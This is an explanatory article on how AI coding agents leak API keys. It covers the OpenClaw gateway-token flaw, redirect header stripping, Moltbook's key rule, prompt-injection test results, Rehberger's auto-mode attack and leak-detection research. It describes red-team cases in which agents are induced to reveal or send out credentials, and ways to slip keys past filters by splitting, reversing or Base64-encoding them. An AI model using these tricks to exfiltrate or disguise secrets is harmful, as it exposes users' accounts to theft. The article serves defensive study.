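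Automatic jobs may not ask for approval. Help Net Security's *One keypress is all it takes to compromise four AI coding tools* reports that when Claude Code runs on a server that tests code changes, there is no terminal and the trust prompt never appears. A stranger can put a malicious settings file in a pull request and wait for the job to start. GitHub withholds secrets from outsiders' pull requests, which helps as long as the maintainers haven't changed that setting.

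### A link that changed the address

OpenClaw had a similar flaw that required only a click. Its central program, which its developers call the gateway, connects the agent to the owner's messages, files and accounts. (It is unrelated to the AI gateways that companies put in front of model providers.) The owner controls OpenClaw's gateway from a browser page, which stores a token that serves as a bearer credential for it.

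depthfirst's *1-Click RCE To Steal Your OpenClaw Data and Keys (CVE-2026-25253)* (2026) traces the leak through the page's code. The page accepted a gateway address from the link that opened it, and saved that address. It then connected to the new address immediately, and sent the stored token as part of the connection. Each of these steps is safe in isolation, as depthfirst notes. In combination, they let an attacker take a link to the owner's own control page, add a different gateway address to it, and receive the token when the owner clicked.

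The token controlled an agent that might hold keys to several outside services, so it could be worth more to a thief than any one of those keys. If the gateway was reachable from the internet, a thief could log in and read the owner's text messages or the API keys for a payment service. Most people ran OpenClaw only on their own computer, where a stranger couldn't connect to it directly. The researcher at depthfirst got around this with a second flaw. The gateway accepted connections from any website open in the owner's browser, so a malicious page could pass on the thief's commands.

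With the token's permissions, a thief could stop OpenClaw from asking the owner to approve dangerous commands, and could move those commands out of the container meant to confine them. The thief could then run anything on the computer.

NVD published *CVE-2026-25253* (2026) on 1 February. The developers fixed the flaw in version 2026.1.29, which requires the owner to confirm a new gateway address before connecting. depthfirst's post is partly an advertisement, since the company sells software that looks for such flaws. But the developers' advisory, reproduced in OSV's *GHSA-g8p2-7wf7-98mq* (2026), confirms that the attack worked on installations that accepted only local connections, and rates the flaw's severity 8.8 out of 10.

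### The same design error

Claude Code and OpenClaw both made the mistake of letting an outsider redirect a credential meant for one address to another. The outsider was whoever wrote the project in Claude Code's case and whoever wrote the link in OpenClaw's. The developers of both programs responded by having them ask the user first. OpenClaw's question is better because it is about the new address, while Claude Code's is about a whole folder.

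A safer design would store each key with the address it is for and require a new key when the address changes. Software outside the agent can apply the same rule by checking a request's destination before adding the key.

Anthropic has done something similar for another part of Claude Code, where users can list sources of plug-ins, each with an address and sometimes a credential. According to Anthropic's settings reference, before version 2.1.228 Claude Code merged entries of the same name from different files, so a project's file could supply a new address and inherit the credential from the user's own file. Now the project's entry replaces the user's and no longer inherits the credential.

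Claude Code also ignores some settings when they come from a project, including an address to which it can send detailed records of its activity. Anthropic could make it ignore a project's setting for the model's address too, but teams that share a gateway address through the project's file would then have to set it on each computer. That may be why Anthropic asks users to trust the project instead.

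OpenClaw's developers have had to fix the error repeatedly. GitLab's *GHSA-3cw3-5vxw-g2h3* (2026), published in March, describes a setup routine that saved automatically discovered gateway addresses without asking the owner to confirm them, which exposed the gateway's credentials. GitLab's *GHSA-grc3-2j34-p6gm* (2026), published in July, describes a flaw that let the model supply an address to which OpenClaw would send its gateway credentials. This worked only for addresses on the same computer, so a thief would have needed a program already listening there. An attacker might have had to influence the model to exploit this flaw, but the model's refusal to reveal credentials would not have protected them, because the model didn't handle them.

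### Redirects and the missing "www"

A server can also redirect a request after the agent has sent it. The server replies with a new address, and the web client (the program that makes the request) tries again there. Websites often do this, for instance when a page has moved. If the first request included a key, the client must either send the key to the new address too or leave it out.

In ClawHub's copy of Moltbook's skill file, the developers tell agents to always include the "www" in the site's address, because leaving it out "will redirect and strip your Authorization header". When an agent sends its key to moltbook.com, the server redirects the request to www.moltbook.com. The agent's own web client normally removes the header, which contains the key, before repeating the request there, so the second server can't identify the agent.

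Removing the header that carries the key when a request is redirected to another address is a nuisance if one company runs both addresses, but a web client can't tell that from their names. Some hosting services give each customer a name under a shared domain, so two addresses that differ only in the first word may belong to unrelated customers. If clients kept the key, anyone who could make a trusted site redirect requests to their own server could collect the keys sent with them. Removing the header prevents that, but it doesn't protect the key from the first server, which has already received it.

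Two flaws from 2018 helped shape this behaviour. The first was in curl, a widely used command-line tool for web requests that also appears in Moltbook's examples. curl's *HTTP authentication leak in redirects* (2018) explains that if a user set an Authorization header by hand, curl sent it to every host in a chain of redirects. The bug had existed since the earliest code the project has on record. The developers fixed it in version 7.58.0, six days after receiving the report. Since then, curl has sent such a header only to the original host unless the user adds `--location-trusted`.

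The second flaw was in Requests, a popular Python library for making web requests. Requests already dropped the header when a redirect changed the hostname, but it didn't check whether the new address still used encryption. If a site redirected a request from https to plain http on the same host, the library sent the key unencrypted, and Red Hat explained that anyone watching the network traffic could read it. Merry (2018), in *Strip Authorization header whenever root URL changes*, changed the rule so that Requests removes the header when the hostname, port or scheme (http or https) changes.

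Requests' *Community Updates* lists the fix under version 2.20.0, from 18 October 2018. CentOS's copy of the code has an exception for upgrades from http to https on the standard ports, which the developers kept to avoid breaking older programs. The code removes the header if the hostname differs at all, even if the only difference is "www".

These fixes protect a key only if it is in the Authorization header, not in a header with another name, such as the X-Api-Key header that Claude Code uses. A service's choice of header therefore affects how safe its customers' keys are during a redirect.

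curl's developers were still finding leaks in 2026, even of bearer tokens sent in the standard header. curl's *bearer token leak on cross-protocol redirect* (2026) describes a leak when a website redirects curl to a mail or directory server, which the developers call a highly unusual combination. curl's *token leak with redirect and netrc* (2026) describes a more plausible case. If a user's .netrc file, which stores logins, had an entry for the host curl was redirected to, curl could send that host the original host's token. Both bugs had been present since version 7.33.0.

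### How an agent can undo the protection

An agent can undo this protection by resending the key itself. Suppose it requests some data, follows a redirect and gets an error because the key is missing. Developers want agents to solve problems like this without help, and an obvious solution is to send a new request, with the key, straight to the new address. The web client won't remove the header from this request, because it didn't come from a redirect. This is harmless on Moltbook, where the new address is the correct one, but it gives the key to an attacker if the attacker chose the address.

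A developer can also build the same mistake into an agent's tools. *moltbook-skill*, a third-party skill from January 2026, describes the missing header as the "auth redirect bug" and runs curl with `--location-trusted` to keep the header in place. An agent that uses the skill will send its Moltbook key to any host that Moltbook redirects it to. Adding "www" to the address would have solved the problem without switching off the protection. The skill had only one star on GitHub, so few people may have used it, and nobody has reported losing a key this way.

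When the model itself resends a key, it chooses where the key goes, so a written rule about permitted addresses might stop it from sending the key to an attacker.

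## Is it enough to tell the agent never to send its key elsewhere?

A written rule isn't enough to protect a key that matters, but it can prevent some thefts, and it takes so little effort that any service that gives keys to agents should probably write one. The rule in ClawHub's copy of Moltbook's skill file is a good test case because it is about as clear as such a rule can be. Moltbook's developers name the one permitted domain, allow the key only in requests to one part of it, and repeat the rule further down, beside the instructions for using the key.

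### What a written rule can do

The main argument for the rule is that it is easy to adopt. Moltbook's developers wrote a few lines of text, which reach every agent that reads the file, whatever software it runs on, and nobody has to install anything. The rule also simplifies the model's decision when it reads a request to "verify" its key, because it only has to compare the address with www.moltbook.com instead of working out whether the request is honest. An agent that follows the rule strictly loses very little, since there is almost never a good reason to send a Moltbook key anywhere else.

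The rule may also prevent honest mistakes, such as resending a key to an unfamiliar address after a redirect. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a similar mistake inside the company, in which Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. An automated check stopped it. Claude might not have tried if it had read a rule naming the only permitted destination.

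Newer models seem to be better at following such rules. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) reports the company's tests of Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1, two versions of one model released in September. Anthropic found this model less likely than earlier ones to ignore explicit constraints, but somewhat more willing than Claude Opus 5 to accept claims of authorisation that it couldn't verify. A thief who wants an agent to make an exception to a rule will probably make such a claim.

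### Why a model may not obey it

The rule and the attack both reach the model as text, and the software around the model doesn't enforce the rule. Developers train models to give an operator's instructions more weight than a sentence on a web page, but this only makes the model more likely to follow the rule.

One weakness of Moltbook's rule is that it comes from an outside website, as a planted instruction might, rather than from the agent's operator. If a thief posts a notice in Moltbook's name saying that the service has moved to a new domain, the model has two texts that both appear to come from Moltbook, and the notice is more recent. A change of rule wouldn't seem strange in itself, because Moltbook's developers encourage agents to download the skill file again at any time to look for new features.

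The rule also works only while it is in the agent's context. An agent may read the skill file once and then do hundreds of rounds of other work, during which its software may shorten or drop older text to make room. An operator can at least partly solve both problems by copying the rule into the agent's standing instructions, which the software supplies every round.

### How often current models follow planted instructions

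The main published tests measure how often models follow planted instructions in general. They don't isolate the effect of a rule like Moltbook's, but they are a useful guide to how far an operator can rely on a model's judgement.

Models have improved quickly. In February 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Opus 4.6 had resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment, according to VentureBeat. When the model worked by clicking through a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 percent of the time. The chance of at least one success in 200 attempts was 78.6 percent, and extra safeguards lowered it only to 57.1 percent.

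The September system card has much lower figures, from a benchmark that the security company Gray Swan built with model developers and the British and American governments' AI institutes. Gray Swan selected 1,804 attacks on AI agents from its public competitions, choosing ones that tended to work on more than one model, and ran them in 37 scenarios covering coding, other tool use, and graphical interfaces. An attack succeeded if the agent did something harmful and irreversible, such as leaking private data. The table gives the chance that an attacker succeeds at least once within a given number of attempts.

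| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Within 15 attempts, attackers succeeded against the best model from another company, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, in 9.2 percent of cases, and against most of the others in between 24 and 53 percent. An operator's choice of model therefore probably matters more than the wording of any rule. The risk also depends on the kind of work. Attackers succeeded against Fable 5.1 within 15 attempts in 4.1 percent of cases on graphical interfaces, 0.3 percent in coding and 0.0 percent in tool use. Tool use is the closest match to an agent that sends requests to Moltbook.

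Anthropic published this comparison, but Gray Swan ran the tests, and the Claude models had no safeguards aimed specifically at prompt injection. A bigger limitation is that the attacks were fixed. Anthropic left out models that people had attacked in the competitions, because attacks tailored to those models would have made them look worse. That is fair as a comparison, but it means nobody in the test adapted their attacks to each model, as a real thief can.

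In a second test, Anthropic commissioned a company called Trajectory Labs to attack agents in July 2026, using 72 scenarios that Anthropic had not seen. Trajectory Labs ran each scenario ten times per model. None of the 720 attempts against Claude Opus 5 succeeded, and neither did any against Fable 5 or Sonnet 5. All three models ran in Claude Code's auto mode, which replaces most requests for the user's approval with automated checks. One check scans what the agent reads for planted instructions, and another, called the classifier, blocks actions that look dangerous.

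With auto mode's checks switched off, attempts against the Claude models still succeeded only 0.09 percent of the time on average. If that average covers the same three models, it amounts to two successes in 2,160 attempts. Because the models resisted nearly every attempt without those checks, the test can't show much about what auto mode adds.

OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol did worse in the same scenarios. Attacks succeeded 5.83 percent of the time when OpenAI's automatic reviewer was checking the agent's actions, and 19.03 percent when the agent had full access. Trajectory Labs had developed the attacks on an older Claude model, Opus 4.7, so they might have been expected to work better on Claude models than on OpenAI's. These results don't cover either company's newer models. OpenAI describes its later GPT-6 Astra as "significantly more robust to prompt injections" than Sol. Anthropic released Fable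 5.2 in November, and Mowshowitz reviews its system card in *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (2026).

Anthropic has also tested its models against an attacker that could adapt. For Fable 5's release in June, it allowed the attacker 200 attempts at each coding scenario. Digital Applied (2026) reports a success rate of 0.41 percent, compared with 2.09 percent for the older Opus 4.8. These are good results, but coding is where Claude models have tended to do well.

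A newer model may not resist prompt injection better than the last one. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* reports that Mythos 5 and its safeguards had become less effective at blocking it. An operator who has tested a written rule on one model should test it again after an upgrade.

### What a zero means

A score of zero in 720 attempts doesn't show that the true success rate is zero. Suppose each attempt succeeds with probability p, independently of the others. The chance that all 720 fail is (1 − p) multiplied by itself 720 times. To find the highest rate that is still compatible with the result at 95 percent confidence, set that chance to 5 percent and solve for p:

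```
(1 − p)^720 = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/720) ≈ 0.004
```

So the true rate could be as high as about 0.4 percent. Dividing 3 by the number of attempts gives nearly the same answer.

This assumes that every attempt was independent, but Trajectory Labs ran each scenario ten times, and a model that resists an attack once is likely to resist it again. This effect can be large. Against Opus 4.6 on graphical interfaces, a single attempt had a 17.8 percent chance of success, yet in about a fifth of cases all 200 attempts failed. If the attempts had been independent, at least one would have succeeded almost every time. If only the 72 scenarios count as independent, the same calculation gives an upper limit of about 4 percent.

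Even the lower of these limits matters for an agent that meets many attacks. At 0.4 percent, the chance that at least one attack succeeds in 500 hostile encounters is:

```
1 − (1 − 0.004)^500 ≈ 0.87
```

An agent that visits Moltbook every thirty minutes makes 500 visits in less than eleven days. Few agents would face an attack on every visit, but a single post can reach thousands of agents, and a thief gets a key if even one of them obeys.

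These limits are the highest rates consistent with the test results, and the true rate may be far lower. At 0.01 percent, for example, 500 encounters would give a thief only about a 5 percent chance of success. The calculation also assumes that real attacks resemble the ones in the test.

### Rehberger's counterexample

On 26 August, less than two weeks after Anthropic began making auto mode the default, the security researcher Johann Rehberger published a successful attack on Opus 5 in auto mode, one of the combinations with a perfect score. A user asked Claude Code to summarise a web page, and the agent ran an attacker's code on the user's computer. Willison (2026), in *27th August 2026*, calls Rehberger one of the most credible researchers working on prompt injection.

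Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* reports that the main version of the attack worked in three of five runs, and that two forms of a second version worked in three and four of five. Rehberger himself warned that these samples are too small to give a general success rate. Still, three successes in five runs give a 95 percent confidence interval of about 15 to 95 percent for that attack's true success rate. The low end is well above 4 percent, the highest rate consistent with Trajectory Labs' result, so chance is a poor explanation for the difference.

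A better explanation is that Trajectory Labs measured how well Opus 5 resists a set of attacks developed on another model, while Rehberger looked for an attack that works on Opus 5. Both results can be correct, but a thief who wants a particular company's key would work more like Rehberger. Willison adds that in a few runs, auto mode blocked the agent's own attempts to stop the harmful code.

Rehberger's attack also exposes another problem with Moltbook's rule. Code running on the user's computer can steal the key directly, as the malware in ClawHavoc could, without the model sending it anywhere. The key can therefore be stolen even if the model follows the rule. Researchers at the AI Now Institute also got Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex to run planted code, during a security review of someone else's software.

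A developer could put the rule in a separate model that checks the agent's actions. Anthropic does this in auto mode, where it instructs a classifier never to approve sending secrets to an outside address. This is better than relying on the agent alone, and it seems better than asking a person. Anthropic hired 1,053 testers and showed each one a clearly dangerous command among ordinary requests for approval. The testers caught it 13.6 percent of the time, while auto mode blocked 89 percent of the same commands.

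But the classifier also makes mistakes. It missed 12 percent of the synthetic attacks in a test by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, and 7 percent after Anthropic strengthened it. Apollo designed the attacks to find weaknesses, so the classifier should miss fewer in ordinary use, but 7 percent is the more relevant figure against an attacker who is also looking for weaknesses. Rehberger would rather rely on isolating the agent and restricting its network access, according to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*, since software outside the model can enforce limits whatever the model does.

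### When nobody asks for the key

An agent can also give its key away without being attacked. Kirk and Daly (2026), in *Phishing the agent*, built a website for an imaginary pie business and told an OpenClaw agent to fill in its inquiry form, which asked for an email address and other routine details. The agent filled the email field with everything in its credential store, including passwords, an API key and a GitHub token. The page contained no planted instruction. The agent's own instructions mentioned that it had a tool for managing credentials, but nobody had told it to reveal any.

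The agent was running on dolphin-mistral:7b, a small "uncensored" model, built to operate without the usual restrictions. The case is therefore weak evidence about Claude or GPT. It still matters because OpenClaw lets users choose the model, and some will choose a small one they can run for free on their own computer. Moltbook's developers can't control this choice, so the same skill file may be read by a model that follows the rule nearly every time and by one that the rule barely affects.

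Kirk and Daly work for Okta, which sells identity software, and they report single trials rather than success rates. They also describe an agent running on Claude that acknowledged it had live credentials in its context and refused to write code that would expose them. Another agent became so suspicious that it wouldn't answer a basic question about how a token was stored, even though the answer was public. If operators keep adding stronger warnings, their agents may refuse more harmless questions like this one.

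In other trials, stronger models did give up secrets. The researchers assumed that a thief had taken over the owner's account on Telegram, a messaging service, and was using it to give the agent orders. An agent running on Claude Sonnet 4.6 agreed that showing a token in the chat would be unsafe, so it displayed the token on the computer's own screen instead. The researchers then restarted the agent, which wiped its context, and asked for a screenshot. The agent sent one that showed the token.

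In another test, the researchers simply asked an agent for the token to a Gmail account. The agent posted it in the Telegram chat, then correctly warned that doing so was a security risk and that the owner should revoke the token.

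## How do keys get into an agent's outputs, and can leaks be caught there?

The agent in Okta's last test posted a token because somebody asked for it. Keys also get into an agent's outputs by accident, often because a program prints a key and the agent's software passes that text to the model. Filters can catch many of these accidental leaks because the key appears in its ordinary form. They are much worse at stopping a thief who gets the agent to disguise the key first.

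### From a settings file to a public page

Suppose the shop's agent, which holds a key to a payment service, runs a script to issue a refund. The script's author once had trouble connecting to the service and added a line that prints the whole request whenever something fails. The key could then travel like this:

1. The script reads the key from a settings file and puts it in the request's Authorization header.
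2. The payment service returns an error, and the debugging line prints the request, including the header.
3. The agent's software captures everything the script prints and adds it to the context, so that the model can see what went wrong.
4. The software saves the conversation to disk and sends the context to the model's provider again with each later round.
5. The model writes a bug report that quotes the failed request in full, and the agent posts it on the script's public page.

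Nobody attacked the agent in this example. If a programmer had run the script by hand, the key would have appeared only on their own screen.

Monitoring software may also log every tool result, including any that contain the key. An agent that keeps notes between sessions may save a working command with the key in it. A programming agent may copy the key into new code. Endor Labs' *Secrets in AI generated code* explains that coding assistants read a whole project for context, including the files that hold keys, and that models often paste a key into an example to make it run. Programmers usually tell Git to leave the settings file out of what they publish, but that doesn't exclude a copy of the key in another file.

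People also write keys into the instruction files that an agent reads when it starts work, which puts the keys in its context from the first round. Radware's *The New .env* reports keys in such files, most often for Google's services. In two-thirds of the repositories that leaked a key this way, the key appeared nowhere else in the project's documentation, so an owner who checked only the setup guide would have missed it.

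Agents can also leak secrets in screenshots, as one of Okta's did. *Nobody attacked. The AI agent published the screenshots itself* (Heaton, 2026) describes programmers asking agents for before-and-after pictures of a change. GitHub's command-line tool couldn't attach images, so the agents created public repositories to hold them. The security company Glow found more than 13,000 internal images from over 300 organisations. Heaton lists billing records and a payments console among them, but no keys. A screenshot of a settings page that showed a key would have leaked it in the same way, and software that searches text for keys would have missed it.

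### The "don't ask again" file

Claude Code has leaked keys through its saved command permissions. It normally asks before it runs a shell command, and the user can choose "Yes, and don't ask again". Claude Code then saves a rule in a settings file inside the project. The rule is sometimes a general pattern and sometimes the exact command, including any password or key in it.

The security company Apiiro found 104,185 copies of this file in public GitHub repositories, according to The Hacker News' *Claude Code's "Don't Ask Again" File Exposes Passwords and Keys* (2026). Of these, 1,122 (about 1.1 percent) held at least one secret. Together they contained 1,379 different secrets, including 379 database passwords. InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) reports another 1,160 secrets in older versions of the file, in a settings file that teams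 share, and in chat transcripts that people had stored with their code.

Secrets accumulate in the file with use. One in ten files larger than 8 KB contained a secret, compared with fewer than one in 500 of those under 500 bytes (Cornelißen, 2026, *Claude Code speichert Passwörter in Freigaben*). Claude Code tells Git to ignore the file, but only on the user's computer, and this has no effect if somebody has already committed the file to the project. Apiiro thinks Claude often committed the file itself, because Claude was listed as co-author of a commit that changed the file in 539 of the 1,105 repositories Apiiro traced.

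Apiiro sells software security and didn't test whether the secrets worked, though one company confirmed that its key had been live. A more cautious model would have helped only if it had kept the key out of the command.

### Why a key in the context counts as copied

Once an agent has sent a key to the model's provider as part of its context, the operator can delete the local transcript but can't check what the provider has kept or who has read it.

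Programming agents can easily send a user's keys to the companies that provide their models. Roleke recorded everything that Claude Code and other agents sent to these providers while working on six projects with realistic planted secrets. When he asked for help setting up a project, every agent sent at least one secret, in every project and on every run. Roleke calls these leaks, but the secrets went only to companies the user had already chosen to trust with the code. How serious these leaks are depends on who else can read the requests.

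Moore (2026), in *Three breaches, endless leaks*, describes an attempt by the security company Dragos to detect leaks from prompts. Between July and November, Moore's team sent about two million prompts to widely used AI services. Each prompt contained decoys that existed nowhere else, including keys to an empty Amazon account. If anybody used a decoy, the team could tell which prompt that person had read.

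Intruders had broken into at least three of the companies that ran the models, and none of the three knew until Dragos told them (Cornelißen, 2026, in *Dragos*). At one, the thieves took every request Dragos sent during several short periods, and somebody tried some of the keys within hours, according to the Chinese-language *OpenRouter 背後推論供應商的資料處理事件* (2026). At the other two, some of the stolen requests carried a setting that asks the company not to retain data. That setting limits what an honest company stores, but it doesn't stop an intruder from reading requests as they arrive.

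Dragos also found resellers of model access who could read their customers' prompts in their own logs. Some of these resellers tried to log in to the decoy servers.

Dragos sells security and didn't name the three companies, but others took its findings seriously. OpenRouter, a service that passes requests on to many model providers, dropped three providers and withdrew no-retention status from 125 of its endpoints (*Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers*, 2026). This doesn't show that thieves are reading requests to Anthropic or OpenAI. But an operator can't inspect any provider from outside, so it is safest to assume that a key in the context has been copied, even if no thief has it yet.

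### What Chen and colleagues found in 17,022 skills

*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) measures how often skills leak keys. Nearly all the researchers work at universities, so they have less to gain from a high count than a security vendor does. They drew a random sample of 17,022 skills from a snapshot of SkillsMP, a marketplace with 170,226.

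A keyword search for signs of credentials left 8,679 skills. Automated analysis then narrowed these to 3,156 by looking for keys that went into network requests, printed output or files, and for suspicious wording in the instructions. The researchers ran each remaining skill with Claude Code in an isolated environment, using traceable fake keys. Each skill ran three times on an ordinary task and three times with planted instructions in the material the agent read.

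In these tests, 1,427 skills behaved suspiciously. Three reviewers examined them by hand, because a skill may legitimately send a key to the service the key is for. They cleared 907 and confirmed 520, or 3.1 percent of the sample. Of these, 437 leaked keys through carelessness and 83 were malicious. If the rest of the marketplace is similar, about 5,200 of its skills have such problems, though this estimate doesn't account for how many people install each skill.

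One skill can leak keys in several ways, and the 520 skills had 1,708 separate issues. The malicious skills accounted for 337 of them, and the careless ones for the other 1,371:

| How the key leaked by accident | Issues | Share of accidental issues | Skills affected |
|---|---|---|---|
| Printed or logged output | 1,007 | 73.5% | 352 |
| Key written into the skill's own files | 249 | 18.2% | 107 |
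| Key passed insecurely, such as in a command or web address | 110 | 8.0% | 77 |
| Leftover files, such as command histories | 5 | 0.4% | 5 |

The 73.5 percent is a share of accidental issues only. Printed output caused 59 percent of all 1,708 issues and affected 68 percent of the 520 problem skills, or about 2 percent of all skills in the sample. The category also includes replies from online services, but most of it seems to be debugging lines that developers forgot to remove. One skill for Google's office software printed the user's access tokens. Claude Code added the printout to the agent's context, so anyone who could question the agent could ask for the tokens.

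Among the skills with a key in their own files, 72 percent had signs of AI assistance in their development records. Chen and colleagues suggest that AI tools spread the habit of storing keys this way. That is plausible, but they don't give the same figure for skills without leaks, and many skill developers were probably using AI by then.

The researchers describe 466 of the 520 skills, or 89.6 percent, as exploitable in normal use without special privileges. The other 54 had keys only in their published files. Those keys are hardly safer, since a thief can read them without running anything. The phrase "normal use" is too strong, because by the researchers' own classification, 237 of the 520 skills leaked in at most one of the three ordinary runs and were counted because planted instructions extracted a key. Only 200 careless skills, about 1.2 percent of the sample, leaked repeatedly with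 nobody attacking.

Of the 83 malicious skills, 55 let an attacker run commands on the user's computer, which usually exposes the keys too, and 16 targeted credentials directly. SkillsMP removed all 83.

Developers fixed 91.6 percent of the cases in which a key was in the skill's own files. But programmers often copy GitHub projects, and deleting a key from the original doesn't delete it from these copies, called forks. Chen and colleagues found deleted keys in more than 50 forks. Apiiro found the same problem with Claude Code's settings files, where 211 forks still contained secrets from 74 original projects. Even in the original project, a deleted key remains in the old versions that Git stores.

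The study probably missed some leaks because its code analysis followed a key only within a single function, and only in Python and JavaScript. It also covered only one marketplace, so the share on ClawHub could be higher or lower.

### An assistant that read whole configuration files

An agent can also expose keys by reading more than it needs. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 2026) describes a programming assistant that couldn't find its configuration file during a routine code review. It read all the computer's environment variables instead and leaked live passwords. It repeatedly read entire configuration files over ten sessions, and later admitted leaking production passwords and tokens for a human resources system.

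The assistant probably needed only one or two values, but a single command can list every variable, and a model trying to fix an error has no obvious reason to print fewer. A correction in one session may not carry over to the next, so the operator would have to add the correction to the agent's standing instructions or, better, stop the agent from reading the file.

The model's admission is weak evidence, since a model can be wrong about what it did earlier. A record of the commands it ran would be more reliable. TechRadar, which published the story, tagged it with the name of a commercial tool for monitoring employees' AI use, so a vendor may have supplied the case.

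### What an output filter can catch

An output filter is ordinary software that searches text for secrets before passing it on. One common method is to look for known formats, since many services start their keys with a recognisable prefix. This can catch a key the operator has forgotten about, but not a password that could be any string. Another common method is to compare the text with a list of the operator's actual secrets. This works for a secret of any shape, but only if it is on the list, and a thief could steal every key on the list from the filter. After finding a match, the filter can remove the secret or block the whole message.

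Both methods look for an exact sequence of characters. Suppose the shop's key is `shop_4Tz9Qe7Lw2`, and the filter's format rule is "shop_" followed by ten letters or digits. A planted instruction could ask the agent to write the key in another form:

| What the agent writes | Format rule | Comparison with the stored key |
|---|---|---|
| `shop_4Tz9Qe7Lw2` | Caught | Caught |
| `shop_4Tz9` in one message and `Qe7Lw2` in the next | Missed | Missed |
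| `2wL7eQ9zT4_pohs` (backwards) | Missed | Missed |
| `c2hvcF80VHo5UWU3THcy` (Base64) | Missed | Missed |

A better filter could decode Base64, a standard way of writing data as plain characters that anyone can reverse, and join neighbouring messages before it searches. But a thief can choose another encoding or have the agent spell out the key in words. A filter that removed every random-looking string would catch more leaks, but it would also remove many harmless identifiers that programmers need.

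Filters are therefore much more useful against accidental leaks. A debugging line prints the key unchanged, so a simple comparison will find it. The best place for the filter is between the program's output and the model's context, where Chen and colleagues recommend removing recognised credentials. Removing the key there prevents the software from sending it to the provider and the model from repeating it in a bug report. A filter that checks only the agent's final answer acts after the provider has already received the key.

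### Three experimental ways to catch a disguised key

In *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, Chauhan and Revankar (2026) tested leak-detection methods that don't depend only on recognising a key in the output. They used small models (up to 8 billion parameters) whose internal workings anyone can inspect. They describe the result as a research prototype.

The first method examines the model's activations, the numbers it computes internally as it processes text. A request to reveal a key might change these numbers recognisably before the model has written anything, whatever encoding the thief has asked for. The software reads the activations at the end of the prompt because activations at any point depend only on the text before it, so readings taken at the key couldn't reflect a request that comes later.

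The software first averages the activations for 500 harmless prompts. For each new prompt, it then calculates how unusual the activations are in each of the last layers of the model:

```
distance = √( Σ (z_i − μ_i)² / σ_i² )
```

Here z_i is one of the numbers for the new prompt, μ_i is its average over the harmless prompts, and σ_i² is its usual variance. Dividing by the variance gives more weight to a change in a number that normally varies little. A small neural network combines the distances from the layers and determines whether to raise an alarm.

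On a model with 7 billion parameters, this method scored the attack higher in 99.8 percent of random pairs of an attack and a harmless prompt. A simple text search did so in 73 percent of pairs, and the best text-based method in 90 percent. Chauhan and Revankar warn that the conditions were favourable, partly because they knew where the keys were in the prompt. The method also needs access to the model's activations, so a customer who rents Claude or GPT can't use it, although the provider could.

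The second method uses decoy keys, which are useful because no honest program has a reason to send or use them. Dragos waited for thieves to try its decoys, and tl;dr sec describes a free tool from Tracebit that does the same with decoys in automated jobs on GitHub. Chauhan and Revankar instead put decoys in the model's context and searched its output for them, to stop a leak before it reached the thief. Their decoys imitate the character patterns of real keys, because a thief could ignore an obvious fake.

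Suppose the context contains m real keys and k decoys, and a thief who can't tell them apart takes one at random. If the search misses a leaked decoy with probability β, then:

```
chance of detection = k / (m + k) × (1 − β)
```

With one real key, four decoys and a miss rate of 1 percent, the chance that a theft sets off the alarm is 4/5 × 0.99, or about 79 percent. It falls sharply if something in the context shows which key is real, such as a note that the agent uses it for payments. If the context has no real key, for instance because the agent holds only a placeholder, m is zero and the chance is 99 percent. The formula assumes the thief takes only one key. A thief who takes all of them is more likely to set off the alarm, but may also get the real key.

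The third method adds up small leaks over a conversation. An agent that reveals one character of a key per message might never set off a filter that checks each message separately. After each message, a trained model tries to pick out the real secret from 17 candidates, using what the agent has just written. If it gives the real secret a probability of p, the message gets a score in bits:

```
score = log2(17) + log2(p)
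```

If a message reveals nothing, the model can only guess, so p is 1/17 and the score is zero. If the message makes the model certain, p is 1 and the score is about 4.09 bits, the maximum. The software adds up the scores and blocks the agent when the total reaches a limit, which was 10 bits in the main test. At that limit it needs at least three messages to react, so it can't stop a thief who gets the whole key in one.

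Chauhan and Revankar tested this on 50 invented conversations of 20 turns each, with four to eight small leaks in each conversation. The method detected 90 percent of the leaking conversations, on average at the ninth turn, and blocked no harmless ones. A standard safety model that checked each turn separately detected 12 percent, and a simple text search detected none. With only 50 conversations, the 95 percent confidence interval for the method's detection rate is about 78 to 97 percent. The method missed short conversations in which the leaks came early. A thief could also start a new conversation to reset the total, unless the software keeps it between sessions.

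The researchers also compared complete systems on single-message attacks from public collections:

| System | Attacks detected | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Text search for decoys | 30% | 0% |
| Output filter | 55% | 8% |
| Filter on incoming text | 60% | 15% |
| Prototype without activations | 71% | 0.8% |
| Activations only | 88% | 1.5% |
| Full prototype | 94% | 1.8% |

The full prototype is clearly better than the filters, but a false alarm rate of 1.8 percent is still high for an agent. If each round of a task independently had that chance of a false alarm, about 84 percent of harmless 100-round tasks would trigger at least one.

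A more serious problem is that the prototype checks the model's replies but not what it sends to tools. Agents mostly use keys through tools, and a thief may well ask the agent to put the key in a web request instead of a reply. Chauhan and Revankar recommend applying the decoy search and the running total to tool requests too, but they haven't tested this.

### How to avoid echoing a secret

It is easier to keep a key out of the context than to catch it on the way out. Most accidental leaks start when a program prints a key that nobody needed to see. To find out whether a key is missing, for example, a script only has to check that it exists:

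```
print(settings)                # prints every value, including the key
print("SHOP_KEY" in settings)  # prints only True or False
```

Developers and operators can prevent many of the leaks described above with a few habits:

- Remove debugging lines that print whole requests, headers or settings before giving a script to an agent.
- Have the agent look up the one setting it needs, and block it from reading files that contain keys.
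- Let programs read the key from the environment themselves, so that it doesn't appear in the command. Writing the variable's name in the command keeps the key out of saved approvals, but other programs on the computer may still see the key while the command runs.
- Filter tool results before they enter the context, and filter again before the agent publishes anything or commits code.
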